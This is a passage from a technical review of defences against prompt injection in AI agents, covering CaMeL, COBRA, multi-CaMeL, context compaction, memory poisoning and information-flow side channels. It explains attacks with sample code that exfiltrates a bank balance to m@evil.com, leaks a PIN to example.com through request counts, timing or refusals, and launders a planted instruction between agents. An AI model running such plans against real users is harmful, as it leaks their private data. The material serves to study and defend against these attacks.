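These measurements date from January 2026, and ordinary agents have improved a lot since. Claude Sonnet 4.5 scored 37.7% under the 15-step limit, and its published score with 50 steps was 58.1%. Yutori's *OSWorld-Verified Leaderboard* (2026) lists Claude Fable 5 at 86.0% in August, with up to 100 steps. CaMeL-NOVA might benefit from better models too. It scored between 65% and 68% on the same 60 tasks with three quite different quarantined models, which suggests that the planner model matters most.

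### STEER-Bench

STEER-Bench, a benchmark from October 2026, tests branch steering more systematically. Zingrillo and colleagues built 101 tasks, including bank transfers, warehouse logistics and changes to a patient's medication. Some tasks appear with several attacks, for a total of 199 attack cases.

Existing agents could run 74 of these cases. Attacks succeeded in 67 (90.5%) against an ordinary agent, in which one model repeatedly looks at the screen and chooses an action. They succeeded in 65 (87.8%) against CaMeL-NOVA, so fixing the plan in advance gave almost no protection here. The researchers ran each case once, so the difference of two cases is very weak evidence that CaMeL-NOVA is safer.

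That doesn't mean fixed plans are useless against prompt injection, because most of these attacks target what a fixed plan leaves open, and CaMeL-NOVA had no policies. One group of attacks tried to add an action that was not in the plan, and 89% of them succeeded against CaMeL-NOVA. This is surprising, since its design should rule out new actions. A possible explanation is that the benchmark scores outcomes, and a click in the plan can have an unintended effect.

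### How COBRA restricts each branch

Zingrillo and colleagues also built COBRA, which checks the effects of a click instead of the click itself. When an agent presses a button on a website, the browser usually sends a request that names the site and the operation, often with further details in separate fields. COBRA reads these requests through a filter between the browser and the internet. A second filter checks calls to tools that use MCP, a common standard for connecting tools to models.

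Suppose the user wants to buy a kettle if it costs at most $50. COBRA would handle the request in these steps:

1. The planner model writes a program with one branch for buying the kettle and another for stopping.
2. Before the agent sees the shop's page, a further call to the planner model adds restrictions to each branch. The buying branch may use only this shop's checkout, and the price field may not exceed $50. The stopping branch may not use the checkout at all.
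3. The agent opens the page, and the quarantined model reports the price as a number.
4. The interpreter compares the number with $50, chooses a branch and activates that branch's restrictions. It removes them again when the agent leaves the branch.
5. The filter compares the outgoing request with the active restrictions.

If the kettle costs $80 and a false label makes the quarantined model return $40, the interpreter takes the wrong branch. The checkout request then contains the real price of $80, and the filter blocks it.

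By default, COBRA's filter restricts only which sites the agent may contact. If the user has approved a description of a site's operations, the filter can also restrict those operations and their fields. In WASP, an older benchmark, 19 attacks tried to make an unauthorised request, and 14 of them stayed on a permitted site. In one of the 14, the user wanted to comment on a software project, and the injection tried to add an access key to another project on the same site. All 14 succeeded when COBRA had no site descriptions, but COBRA blocked all 19 attacks when it had them.

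Few websites publish such descriptions. Zingrillo and colleagues wrote a program that drafts them by exploring a site, and its drafts covered every necessary operation for 18 of 25 web tasks. Someone still has to review the drafts and update them when the site changes.

### COBRA's results

No attack on STEER-Bench succeeded against the complete system. The researchers then repeated each attack with the protection it targeted switched off.

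| Protection switched off | Attacks | Success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Limits on the values in a request | 26 | 100% |
| Limits on sites and operations | 24 | 100% |
| Filter for tool calls | 15 | 67% |
| Shared limits for web requests and tool calls | 72 | 100% |
| Checks on where required values come from | 33 | 55% |
| Detection of changed site or tool descriptions | 5 | 80% |
| Separation of planning from the screen | 9 | 67% |
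| Removal of a branch's permissions afterwards | 10 | 100% |
| Combined limits in nested branches | 5 | 80% |

In total, 174 of the 199 attacks succeeded, so COBRA's 0% was not simply due to weak attacks. Where the success rate was below 100%, something else, such as another of COBRA's checks, stopped some of the attacks. One group accounts for 72 of the attacks, but without it the success rate would still be 80%.

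On STEER-Bench, COBRA kept 97% of the benign utility, the ability to complete tasks when there is no attack, and blocked legitimate actions in 4 of 138 runs. It can lose more utility on other tasks. On 361 desktop tasks, Claude Sonnet 5 completed 51.0% as an ordinary agent and 38.8% when it filled both roles in COBRA, with up to five attempts in each case. It completed about a quarter fewer tasks with COBRA mainly because a planner that can't see the screen has trouble preparing for everything that may appear there.

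The 97% also excludes requests that left out an essential value. COBRA is supposed to ask the user for the value before it starts, and it did so in 20 of 22 cases. In a follow-up test, COBRA completed 10 of 11 attack-free tasks when the simulated user typed the missing value. It completed none when the user told it to use the record on file. It stopped safely each time, but a user who wants an order sent to the saved address would have to type the address.

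COBRA also relies on the planner model to turn the request into correct restrictions. Zingrillo and colleagues checked 30 cases by hand and found the restrictions correct in 28. In the other two, the restrictions blocked an action the user had authorised in one case and allowed one the user had not authorised in the other.

### What correct restrictions still allow

COBRA limits what the agent may do in a branch, but it doesn't guarantee that the agent has entered the right branch. Suppose the user asks the agent to pay a seller $200 once a parcel has arrived. If a false delivery notice appears on the screen, the interpreter enters the payment branch, and the agent sends $200 to the right seller for a parcel that hasn't arrived. The payment satisfies every restriction. COBRA's planner model is supposed to notice that the payment depends on an untrusted observation and ask the user beforehand.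 However, Zingrillo and colleagues say that they tested missing values, and that these tests don't show that COBRA can reliably verify facts of this kind.

COBRA doesn't count permitted requests either, so it could allow the same payment twice. This might happen without an attacker if a tool call takes effect but its confirmation gets lost, because the plan may then retry the payment through the website. The researchers did not test this case.

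Some important values never reach the filters. A shop's checkout request may contain only the product's number, not its price. COBRA can then check the $50 limit only against the price that the quarantined model reads from the page, where an advertisement or a customer review can display a false one.

Desktop programs can also act without web requests or MCP calls. A mail program may send messages through SMTP, the standard protocol for email, and a word processor writes directly to the disk. In one outside benchmark, 30 of 51 attacks used channels like these. COBRA still stopped them because they needed actions that were not in the plan. If the user's task did include sending an email from a desktop program, neither filter would detect a changed recipient.

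Across four outside benchmarks, COBRA blocked 1,289 of 1,312 attacks. Of the 23 it did not block, eight were of kinds it was not designed to stop, such as attacks that exploit bugs in the software connecting the tools. In 13, a compromised tool server received the same request an uncompromised server would have received and did something harmful with it. The last two depended on the wording of a text that the agent was allowed to post. As with the email to John Doe, the text went to the right place through a permitted operation, and no rule specified its content.

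## How untrusted text comes to be treated as trusted

In the attacks described so far, the labels were correct but the rules allowed untrusted data through. If an attacker's text is wrongly labelled as trusted, even a rule that refuses untrusted data will accept it. A data-flow defence therefore has to label each piece of data correctly when it enters the system, and every program that later copies, summarises or stores the data has to keep that label.

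Narisetty and colleagues found the first step under-specified in every system they surveyed, and they expect real deployments to fail there. *Utility Under Attack* (2026), a study of attacks on agents' stored memory, labels data as trusted or untrusted according to the channel it arrived on. Software can identify the channel without judging the content, which makes labelling possible, but the label will be wrong whenever an attacker's text arrives on a trusted channel.

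### Wrong labels from the start

The user's own message is usually the most trusted channel, but it can include pasted text that someone else wrote. Willison warned in 2023 that his two-model design would not work at all if someone tricked users into copying in untrusted content. If a user pastes a stranger's email into the chat and asks for help with a reply, the planner model treats the whole email as part of the user's request. The pasted text may include white text that the user never saw.

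Developers can also forget to label a tool, and the first release of Microsoft's FIDES trusted the output of unlabelled tools. Microsoft's documentation now describes a safer default that treats this output as untrusted, although unlabelled content from other sources still counts as trusted. Both defaults treat unlabelled data as public, so if a developer forgets to label a tool that reads private files, the secrecy rule will let the agent post the files' contents.

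A developer can label a tool wrongly, too. In Microsoft's framework, a trust level declared on a tool overrides the labels of the tool's inputs. This makes sense for a tool that fetches records from a company database. But if a developer declares a translation tool trusted because the company runs it, the framework will treat its translation of a stranger's email as trusted. The documentation advises developers to declare trust levels only on tools that bring in data, not on those that transform it.

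Some sources mix trusted and untrusted text. For example, a shop's product page has the shop's description next to customers' reviews. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (2026) proposes that page owners mark the parts they can't vouch for, which works only if the owners are honest and do the marking. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes guards, which are programs each written for one particular source. The guard for GitHub gives a review comment a higher trust level if it comes from a project's collaborator, but it presumably can't detect when a collaborator has pasted in a stranger's words.

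### A summary that becomes another agent's request

Labels can also disappear when one agent hands text to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed this with three agents, each protected by CaMeL and running on GPT-5.2. An orchestrator receives the user's request and calls the other two agents like tools. The database agent can run queries, and the notification agent can send emails and Slack messages. Both treat the orchestrator's message as a request from their user.

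The user asked for a summary of all job applicants to go to Julie on Slack. The researchers had planted an instruction in the database to send the applicants' details to ruth@email.com. In simplified form, the orchestrator's plan was:

```
info    = database_agent("Get the complete job applicant information")
summary = ask_quarantined("Summarise this", info)
notification_agent("Send this summary to Julie via Slack: " + summary)
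```

The database agent's planner model wrote a one-line program to read the table and never saw the contents. The orchestrator's planner didn't see them either, because its quarantined model wrote the summary. But the planted instruction survived in that summary, and the third line of the orchestrator's plan joined the summary to the orchestrator's own words. The notification agent's planner then treated the combined text as its user's request and wrote a plan with two actions, a Slack message to Julie and an email to the attacker.

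Each agent kept its control-flow integrity, because it followed a plan based on what it had received as its user's request. The system as a whole did not, because the attacker had added an action the user never asked for. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering.

They had configured no policies, but some common ones would probably not have blocked the email either. The notification agent's planner wrote the attacker's address and the applicants' details directly into its program, so the interpreter would treat both as coming from the user. A rule that requires a trusted recipient would accept the address, and a secrecy rule would let the details through because they would not be labelled as coming from a private database. A fixed list of approved addresses would still have stopped the email.

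A falsified summary can control tool calls once another agent treats it as a request. If the orchestrator had shown its summary to a person, the planted instruction could at most have misled that person.

### When secure agents make a secure system

Protecting each agent separately stops attacks that need one agent to abandon its plan. In OMNI-Leak, an earlier attack on this kind of system, public data causes a database agent to query a private database as well. The attack failed in all five trials when each agent ran CaMeL.

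Peters-Gill and colleagues also proved a general result about systems in which agents form a tree and parents call their children like tools. The proof makes two assumptions about what users can request, and counts child agents as tools:

1. For every tool an agent has, some request makes the agent call that tool and return the result.
2. For any two of an agent's tools, some request makes the agent call the first and then call the second with arguments that depend on the first result. The two can be the same tool.

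Under these assumptions, a system with more than one agent and at least one tool that returns untrusted data lacks control-flow integrity, even if each of its agents has it.

The proof has two cases. If the agent with the untrusted tool has a child agent, some request makes it call the tool and put the result into the child's instructions. If it has a parent agent, some request makes the parent ask it for the data and then call it again with instructions that contain that agent's answer. In both cases, an agent writes its plan after reading untrusted text.

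The assumptions are mild, since people build these systems largely to pass results from one step to the next. But the proof shows only that at least one request opens the gap. It also doesn't apply to a system whose agents can send each other only fixed instructions, because such a system doesn't meet the second assumption.

### Separate channels for instructions and data

The researchers' solution, multi-CaMeL, splits each message between agents into two parts. The orchestrator's last line becomes:

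```
notification_agent(
    message="Send the provided summary to Julie via Slack.",
    variables={"summary": summary})
```

The notification agent's planner reads only `message`. It can write a plan that fetches `summary` and sends it to Julie without seeing its contents, much like a parameterised database query. The interpreter enforces the separation by rejecting any `message` that depends on a tool's output. The variables also keep their labels, so the receiving agent can apply policies to them.

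*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) describes a similar precaution for results that a sub-agent returns to the outer agent. The sub-agent reads untrusted data and returns a result with its label attached, so the outer agent's own label doesn't change.

Multi-CaMeL doesn't prevent branch steering, and its guarantee covers only trees of agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues leave open how to protect agents that share a memory or send messages to each other freely.

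### What the new protocol costs

To test the protocol, the researchers built MultiAgentDojo, which divides AgentDojo's tools among two to four specialised agents under an orchestrator. They ran 949 attacks for each combination of model and protection level, and separately measured how many of the 97 ordinary tasks the system completed when not under attack.

| Model | Attack success, no CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL | Tasks completed, no CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
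|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 69.1% | 53.6% | 52.6% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 86.6% | 73.2% | 66.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% | 78.4% | 38.1% | 24.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% | 76.3% | 42.3% | 26.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 27.8% | 13.4% | 7.2% |
| Average | 12.9% | 0.2% | 0.0% | 67.6% | 44.1% | 35.5% |

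Every attack that succeeded against individually protected agents used boundary laundering. Only about nine succeeded in 4,745 runs, so the drop from 0.2% to 0.0% with multi-CaMeL is weak evidence by itself. The better reason to trust multi-CaMeL is that its interpreter closes the route these attacks took. The 0.2% may also understate the danger of protecting agents individually, because the injections came from a benchmark for single agents, and an attacker who knew about the hand-over could write one aimed at it.

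On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL in each agent lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average. Multi-CaMeL lowered it by a further 3.2 points, which fits Peters-Gill and colleagues' description of the further loss as modest. On MultiAgentDojo, the further loss averages 8.7 points, and it is 13 to 16 points for GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro. Newer models lose less. Fable 5's scores are low mainly because it refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks, perhaps because it associated the benchmark with attacks. Of the other 45, it completed 91.1% without CaMeL and 84.4% with either version.

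Some completed tasks may also be less useful than the scores suggest. In one, the user wants to send Dora and Eve feedback on their websites. With CaMeL in each agent, the orchestrator pasted Dora's page into its message to the Slack agent, which obeyed an injection on the page and sent a link to Alice. In the multi-CaMeL example, no agent sent the link, but the planner had written the feedback before any agent opened the sites. The feedback praised the "clean design" of a page that contained little besides Dora's email address and the injection. The researchers describe this task as completed.

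### Shortened conversations

A single agent can cause the same problem by summarising its own conversation. Models can read only a limited amount of text at once, so when a conversation gets too long, the agent's software has a model summarise the earlier turns and continues from the summary. This is called compaction. In *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026) recorded 1,108 automatic compactions in the coding agents Claude Code and Codex, and every time the software inserted the summary as a message from the user.

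This matters most for defences that base their rules on the user's request. Progent, for example, uses a model to read the latest user message and write a list of permitted tool calls. In one of the researchers' examples, a user asks a banking agent about their spending in March, and one of the transactions contains an instruction to pay the attacker. Progent blocks the payment because a question about spending doesn't call for one. After compaction, the summary lists the blocked payment as unfinished work. Progent then treats the summary as the user's request, and the only transfer it permits is the payment to the attacker.

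Progent's own integrations write the policy only once per session, which would prevent this. Fei and colleagues had Progent write a new policy for each request because a fixed policy made the agent much less useful. The agent completed the second task in 7 of 60 sessions with a fixed policy, compared with 41 when Progent rewrote the policy for each request.

Newer models are good at detecting injected instructions when they write these summaries. GPT-5.4-mini and GPT-5.5 flagged the injection in 219 of the 220 summaries that kept the attacker's account details or address, but they rarely flagged false information written as ordinary data. In another test, the user gave the agent their landlord's account number and asked what a notice said. The notice, which came from the attacker, gave a different account number but contained no instructions. After compaction, the user asked the agent to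 pay the rent.

The policy based on the summary allowed payment to the attacker's account in 290 of 320 cases. When GPT-5.5 wrote the policy, it allowed the payment in 59% of cases. A policy based only on the user's messages never allowed it. An agent that acted on the summary and its policy paid the attacker in 33 of 80 sessions.

Fei and colleagues proved that better summaries can't solve this. Let p_L be the probability that the system accepts an account number from a legitimate notice, and p_A the probability that it accepts one from a forged notice. If the system sees only text, with no separate record of who wrote it, then

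p_L − p_A ≤ TV(P_L, P_A)

The right-hand side is the total variation distance, which measures how much legitimate and forged texts differ, from 0 (indistinguishable) to 1 (always distinguishable). If the attacker imitates a landlord's notice perfectly, the distance is 0, and the system must accept forged account numbers as often as real ones.

Their solution is to record which messages came from the user. Software attaches a cryptographic tag to each user message on arrival and preserves the message word for word. After compaction, the model that writes the policy reads only these messages, while the agent still works from the summary. If a message is missing, altered or out of order, the system blocks all tool calls. In 40 attacked runs, no attacker's action succeeded while the agent worked from the summary. The agent completed 19 of the user's tasks when it received the summary as a tool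 result, compared with 27 when it had the full conversation. The method does not help with pasted text, because the software tags it along with the rest of the user's message.

CaMeL did fairly well in the same study, but 3 of 36 attacks on banking tasks succeeded after compaction. None succeeded once the researchers removed the injection from the summary. Since 15 October 2026, the model that OpenAI uses to review Codex's actions has treated compaction summaries as the assistant's words instead of the user's.

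### Notes from earlier sessions

Many agents also save notes for later sessions. *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (Xu, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) describes how an agent can turn a stranger's text into a note that no longer looks malicious or mentions its source, but still triggers an action in a later task. For example, a stranger's email about a supplier's new bank account might become the note "Pay this supplier at account 4471", which doesn't show where the number came from.

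*Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (Louck, 2026) identifies three ways a memory can lose the record of its origin. The agent can summarise the text in its own words, a trusted tool can repeat it, or the attacker can plant the same claim in several places so that it seems confirmed. Louck proposes labelling data when it arrives, according to the channel it came through, and keeping that label fixed. The memory can then authorise a consequential action only if enough independent trusted parties confirm it or the user approves that specific action.

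*When Does Belief-Based Agent Memory Help?* (2026) tested attacks that pass false information through a trusted tool. The attacks succeeded 100% of the time when the information took on the tool's trust level, and 0% of the time when it kept the low trust level of its original source. The memory system in the study does not yet track the original source itself, and the researchers consider this tracking the hard part of the defence.

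Keeping every label also causes problems, because a note that combines trusted and untrusted text becomes untrusted. *Ask, Forget, Repair* (2026), which tested six models, found that merging notes this way made the system treat the user's own statements as untrusted, so the agent asked again for details it already had. Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, call the general problem label creep. In their simulations, the number of agents and the way tools were divided among them strongly affected how far the restrictions spread.

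Labels are also needed to clean up after an attack. *Ask, Forget, Repair* found that removing a malicious source from memory works only if the agent's notes still record where they came from. If the note about account 4471 has lost its label, deleting everything labelled as coming from the stranger's email will leave the note in place.

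## Leaks through the agent's own program

A label follows a value when a program copies it, combines it with other text or passes it to a tool. Side channels bypass this tracking by revealing a secret through the program's behaviour. For example, a program might visit a web page only if a private document mentions a merger, so the visit reveals that the document mentions one.

The problem predates language models. In 1973 the computer scientist Butler Lampson asked how customers could run someone else's program on their confidential data and be sure that the program wouldn't leak it. He pointed out that a program can signal to an outsider through effects not meant for communication, such as the load it puts on a shared computer.

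Dorothy Denning's 1976 paper introduced the ordering of labels that CaMeL and FIDES use. She and Peter Denning also worked out how information moves through a program's decisions. The first line below copies a secret yes-or-no value directly, which is called an explicit flow. The other lines produce the same result through a decision, making it an implicit flow.

```
copy = secret

if secret:
    copy = True
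else:
    copy = False
```

A program has noninterference if changing data with one label changes nothing visible to an observer who sees only data with other labels. Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer named the property in 1982. For secrecy, it means that two runs with the same public inputs but different secrets must produce the same public results. The strength of the guarantee depends on what the observer is assumed to see. If the definition covers only the final result, a program that satisfies it may still leak secrets through its running time.

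Noninterference also applies to trust, where it requires that changing an attacker's text not change anything labelled trusted. Branch steering violates this because a false observation changes which actions the agent takes. Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge that multi-CaMeL lacks noninterference for this reason.

### Requests, errors and elapsed time

Suppose `code` is a four-digit PIN from the user's private notes, and the attacker owns the site example.com. This loop gives the attacker the PIN:

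```
for i in range(code):
    get_web_page("https://example.com/tick")
```

If the PIN is 4071, the site receives 4,071 requests. Each contains the same trusted, public address, so a rule that checks only the address allows them all. A legitimate plan can leak in the same way on a smaller scale. If the user asks the agent to look up an exchange rate for each foreign invoice, the owner of the exchange-rate site can count the invoices.

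An error can also reveal a secret:

```
check = 1 / (code - 4071)
get_web_page("https://example.com/done")
```

The division fails only if the PIN is 4071, in which case the plan stops and the request never arrives. An attacker might be able to cause such an error with planted text. Suppose the quarantined model reads a confidential report and the attacker's email in one prompt and must return a date. The email can instruct it to return something other than a date if the report mentions a merger. If the model does so, the type check fails, and the attacker notices that the plan's next visible step is missing.

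The third example uses time:

```
start = clock()
for i in range(code):
    pass
elapsed = clock() - start
get_web_page("https://example.com/?t=" + str(elapsed))
```

The loop does nothing except take longer for a larger PIN. The program calculates `elapsed` from two clock readings, neither of which comes from the PIN, so the label on `elapsed` is public.

According to Narisetty and colleagues, the CaMeL paper demonstrates two working leaks in CaMeL, one through an indirect dependency and one through an error that the attacker triggers, and concludes that the system is vulnerable to side-channel attacks. The timing example fails because CaMeL's interpreter has no clock.

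Ordinary tracking labels a value according to the data used to compute it. CaMeL's strict mode, which handles the other two examples, also adds the labels of the data that determined whether a line of code would run. The PIN determines how often the loop repeats, so every line inside the loop gets the label {S}, for secret. The policy can then refuse the request because it depends on private data.

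Errors need the same treatment, since a line after a division runs only if the division succeeded. This can be very restrictive, because if every step on private data might fail, then every later step depends on private data, even steps that would reveal nothing interesting.

Removing the clock stops the plan from measuring time, but an attacker can still measure it from outside. If a plan opens a page on the attacker's site, runs a loop whose length depends on the PIN and then opens another page, the attacker or someone watching the network can time the gap.

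### The branch the program doesn't take

In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) found a gap in how CaMeL tracks decisions. Their example is a plan that tries to tell an outsider whether the user's bank balance is above some threshold. CaMeL blocks the direct version:

```
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The condition reads the balance, so the email depends on a secret. But a plan can store the result of the condition in variables first. The following version, based on an example that J. S. Fenton published in 1974, gets past the check:

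```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL raises a variable's label when the program assigns to it under a condition that depends on secret data. If the program skips the assignment, the label doesn't change.

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
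| Start | `tmp` and `rich` are True, both { } | `tmp` and `rich` are True, both { } |
| First `if` | `tmp` becomes False, with label {S} | Skipped, so `tmp` stays True, with label { } |
| Second `if` | Skipped, so `rich` stays True, with label { } | `rich` becomes False, with label { } |
| Third `if` | The email goes out | No email |

In both runs, `rich` holds the right answer about the balance but is labelled public. When the balance is high, the program skips the second assignment because of a secret value, and CaMeL has no assignment at which to record that dependence.

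An attacker can't insert these lines into a fixed plan, and an honest planner is unlikely to write this particular program. But the same gap affects more natural plans. Suppose the user asks the agent to look at a shop's offers unless their account is overdrawn:

```
overdrawn = False
if account.balance < 0:
    overdrawn = True
if not overdrawn:
    get_web_page("https://shop.example/offers")
```

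If the account is in credit, the program skips the assignment and `overdrawn` keeps its public label. The interpreter then allows the visit, from which a shop that knows about the plan can infer that the user has money.

Trust labels have the same problem. If a condition depends on a stranger's email, the email can determine a variable's value while the variable remains labelled trusted. Peters-Gill and colleagues note that multi-CaMeL inherits this flaw because it extends CaMeL's interpreter.

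A planner can also give untrusted data a lot of control through ordinary branches. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL without policies, one task asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner wrote a loop with a branch for each tool, so an attacker who wrote the file could choose which tools the program called without adding any code to it.

### Stopping the run

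Thomas Austin and Cormac Flanagan proposed a remedy in 2009, called the no-high-upgrade rule. It stops any run that would change a public variable under a secret condition. Let pc be the combined label of the conditions that led to the current line. The program may then assign to a variable x only if

pc ⊑ label(x)

In the example with two variables, if the balance is high, the program reaches the line `tmp = False` with pc labelled {S} and `tmp` labelled { }. Since {S} may not flow to { }, the run stops there. If the balance is low, the program skips that line, sets `rich` to False and finishes. The outsider receives no email in either case.

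Garby and colleagues apply this rule in the LLMbda calculus, their small programming language for agents. Its programs can change the conversation with the model, so the conversation needs a label, just as a variable does. In one of their examples, a program tells the model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model to set x to true. Finally, it asks the model for x.

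Without the rule, the program could leave the conversation labelled public when the secret is false and raise its label only when the secret is true. The public answer "false" would then reveal the secret. LLMbda stops the run when the program tries to send the conditional message. A programmer can prevent the stop by labelling the conversation secret from the start, but then the answer is secret too.

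Another solution is to inspect the branch the program skips and raise the labels of all variables that branch might have changed. This should be possible for simple CaMeL plans, because the interpreter has the whole program before running it. It is harder in LLMbda, where the model can write new code while the program runs, so the code in the skipped branch may not exist yet.

### Why a refusal reveals something

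Someone may notice when a program stops. In the plan about the shop's offers, the new rule stops the run if the account is overdrawn, so the agent visits the shop only if the account is in credit. The shop therefore learns whether the account is in credit, just as it did before the rule.

The rule still helps, because the secret can no longer change the public result of a run that finishes. If an outsider sees only whether a run finished and its public result, a deterministic program can reveal at most one bit about the secret by stopping. Most formal guarantees allow this leak and are called termination-insensitive, meaning that a secret may influence whether a program finishes.

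Leaking one bit may be tolerable, but when a plan fails, CaMeL's outer loop can get a new one from the planner model and try again. Garby and colleagues point out that this loop is ordinary Python outside the interpreter that tracks labels. The loop has access to whether the policy blocked the last attempt. That result may depend on a secret, but the next attempt starts without the secret's label.

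A program that can choose its next question on the basis of the last refusal can therefore find the whole secret. Suppose `run_plan(middle)` returns True if a policy blocks the plan, which happens only when the PIN is greater than `middle`:

```
low, high = 0, 9999
while low < high:
    middle = (low + high) // 2
    if run_plan(middle):
        low = middle + 1
    else:
        high = middle
```

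Each run halves the remaining possibilities. A four-digit code has 10,000 possible values, so it contains

log₂ 10,000 ≈ 13.3 bits

If each run leaks one yes-or-no answer, 14 runs are enough to identify any four-digit code, because 14 answers can distinguish 2¹⁴ = 16,384 values and there are only 10,000 codes. Thirteen runs would not always be enough, since they distinguish only 2¹³ = 8,192 values. Making the secret longer adds little protection, as 20 runs are enough for any six-digit code and 54 for any sixteen-digit number.

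A limit on retries would reduce the damage. Ten runs can produce at most 1,024 patterns of success and failure. That would narrow the 10,000 codes to about ten on average, so an attacker could still guess the PIN within a few attempts.

An honest CaMeL planner has no reason to search for a PIN like this, but an attacker might be able to run the search from outside by sending a series of emails. Each email would tell the quarantined model to return an invalid answer if the PIN is above a certain number, and the attacker would watch whether the agent took its next visible action. The attack would need only 14 emails and no retry loop, but the agent would have to process the PIN and each email in the same prompt, which is a strong condition.

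CaMeL censors error messages to reduce what its retry loop reveals, but Garby and colleagues note that this has no formal guarantee. The agent they built in LLMbda instead tests its plans on artificial data. During these tests, reading a file always returns the same placeholder text, and payments have no effect. The planner repairs its program until it works, then writes a final version for the real data. Errors during the tests can't reveal the user's secrets because the program hasn't received any.

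Practice doesn't reveal every problem. An unusual file may cause an error only during the real run, when the agent can no longer repair the plan. Practice also doesn't raise label violations, so a plan may work on the artificial data and then violate a policy in the real run. Even so, the agent completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did without its policies.

### The theorem about LLMbda programs

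Garby and colleagues proved a form of noninterference for every LLMbda program. They compared the probabilities of different results rather than the results of single runs, because a language model's replies are random.

Let μ(q) be the probability that a program finishes with result q, as seen by an observer who may read data up to label m. These probabilities can add up to less than 1, because the program may run forever or a check may stop it. The missing part is the probability of not finishing:

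div μ = 1 − Σ μ(q)

Write C for the conversation so far and e for the program, including its data. The notation C₀ ∼ₘ C₁ means that two conversations look the same to this observer, and e₀ ∼ₘ e₁ means the same for two programs. For example, the programs may contain different secret PINs but be otherwise identical. Let μ and ν be the probabilities of their results. The theorem states that

C₀ ∼ₘ C₁ and e₀ ∼ₘ e₁ ⟹ μ ⌣ ν

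The symbol ⌣ means "compatible". Two sets of probabilities are compatible if there is a third set, ω, that has a total of at most 1 and is at least as large as both of them for every result. In other words, either set could become ω if some of its unfinished runs finished.

This limits how much the visible results can differ. The usual measure of the difference is

Δ = ½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)|

and Garby and colleagues proved that

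Δ ≤ (div μ + div ν) / 2

For each result, |μ − ν| equals twice the larger of μ and ν, minus their sum. The larger values add up to at most 1, because ω is at least as large as each of them. The total of |μ − ν| is therefore at most 2 − (1 − div μ) − (1 − div ν), which is div μ + div ν. Halving this gives the bound.

If a program always finishes, both probabilities of not finishing are zero, so Δ is zero and each result has the same probability whatever the secret is.

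A short program reaches the bound. The secret is either "heads" or "tails", and the program makes a random public guess:

```
guess = flip_coin()
if guess != secret:
    stop()
return guess
```

| Secret | Returns "heads" | Returns "tails" | Doesn't finish |
|---|---|---|---|
| Heads | ½ | 0 | ½ |
| Tails | 0 | ½ | ½ |

The two sets of probabilities are compatible, since ω can give each result a probability of ½. The difference is Δ = ½(½ + ½) = ½, which equals the bound of (½ + ½)/2 = ½. The program therefore satisfies the theorem, yet it returns a public answer in half of all runs, and that answer is always the secret. Someone who can run the program repeatedly will soon learn the secret.

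This example also shows why the definition has to be complicated. Garby and colleagues first tried comparing only the runs that finish. Among those runs, one secret always gives "heads" and the other always gives "tails", so the program would fail the test even though the secret affects only whether it finishes.

Δ measures differences only between results that appear. Suppose a program always finishes for one secret and never finishes for another. Δ is then ½, which again equals the bound, but an observer who notices the missing result can tell the two secrets apart every time.

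### What the Lean proof covers

Garby and colleagues checked their proofs with Lean, a program that verifies mathematical arguments. The theorem covers all LLMbda programs, including those in which the agent runs code written by the model. It holds however the software interprets a malicious reply, because any code from a conversation runs with that conversation's label.

The proof also covers the interpreter, which Garby and colleagues wrote in Lean. They proved that it produces results with the probabilities described by the mathematical model, so the guarantee applies to the software that runs the agent. The guarantee assumes that each reply from the language model is drawn independently, with probabilities that depend only on the conversation. The proof does not cover the code that contacts the language model over the network, which it treats as a function that takes a conversation and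 returns a reply.

CaMeL has no comparable theorem, and the paper calls formalisation a crucial direction for further work. Garby and colleagues found another mistake while studying its interpreter. When an untrusted value is inserted into fixed text, the interpreter marks the result as trusted. If a plan inserted a stranger's account number into the sentence "Pay account …", the number would therefore lose its untrusted label through an ordinary explicit flow. A proof about the whole interpreter rules out both mistakes like this one and the harder cases with branches.

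LLMbda also has a command called `endorse`, which changes a value's label from untrusted to trusted. The agent needs it for tasks such as paying a bill whose details are in a file. According to a second theorem, `endorse` can't make secrets public, even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted data. Endorsing a secret password, for instance, leaves its {S} label in place. The command also has no effect inside code that runs because of untrusted data. But if the planner endorses an account number from a file, the theorem doesn't guarantee that the number is correct.

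The proof does not cover timing, because the observer in the theorem sees only a program's final state, not how long the program took or what happened along the way. Garby and colleagues list as a related limitation that they model tools and data sources as part of the program instead of as outside systems.

This matters when a tool acts immediately. Consider a program that visits a page before testing each possible PIN:

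```
for guess in range(10000):
    get_web_page("https://example.com/tick")
    if guess == code:
        stop()
```

The program always stops before returning a result, so someone who sees only final results learns nothing. But the site's owner can count the requests. If the PIN is 4071, the site receives 4,072 requests, one for each guess from 0 to 4071, and the attacker learns the whole PIN in a single run. The limit of one bit per run therefore holds only if nobody sees the program's actions before it finishes. Aslan Askarov, Sebastian Hunt, Andrei Sabelfeld and David Sands described this kind of leak in 2008.

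### What FIDES leaves untracked

For FIDES, Costa and colleagues chose a weaker formal guarantee, called explicit secrecy, which covers only the direct copying of secrets into tool calls.

Let d₁ and d₂ be two versions of the stored data that differ only in their secrets, and let =ʟ mean that two versions have the same public parts. Let g be the effect of the steps the agent actually took. Explicit secrecy requires that

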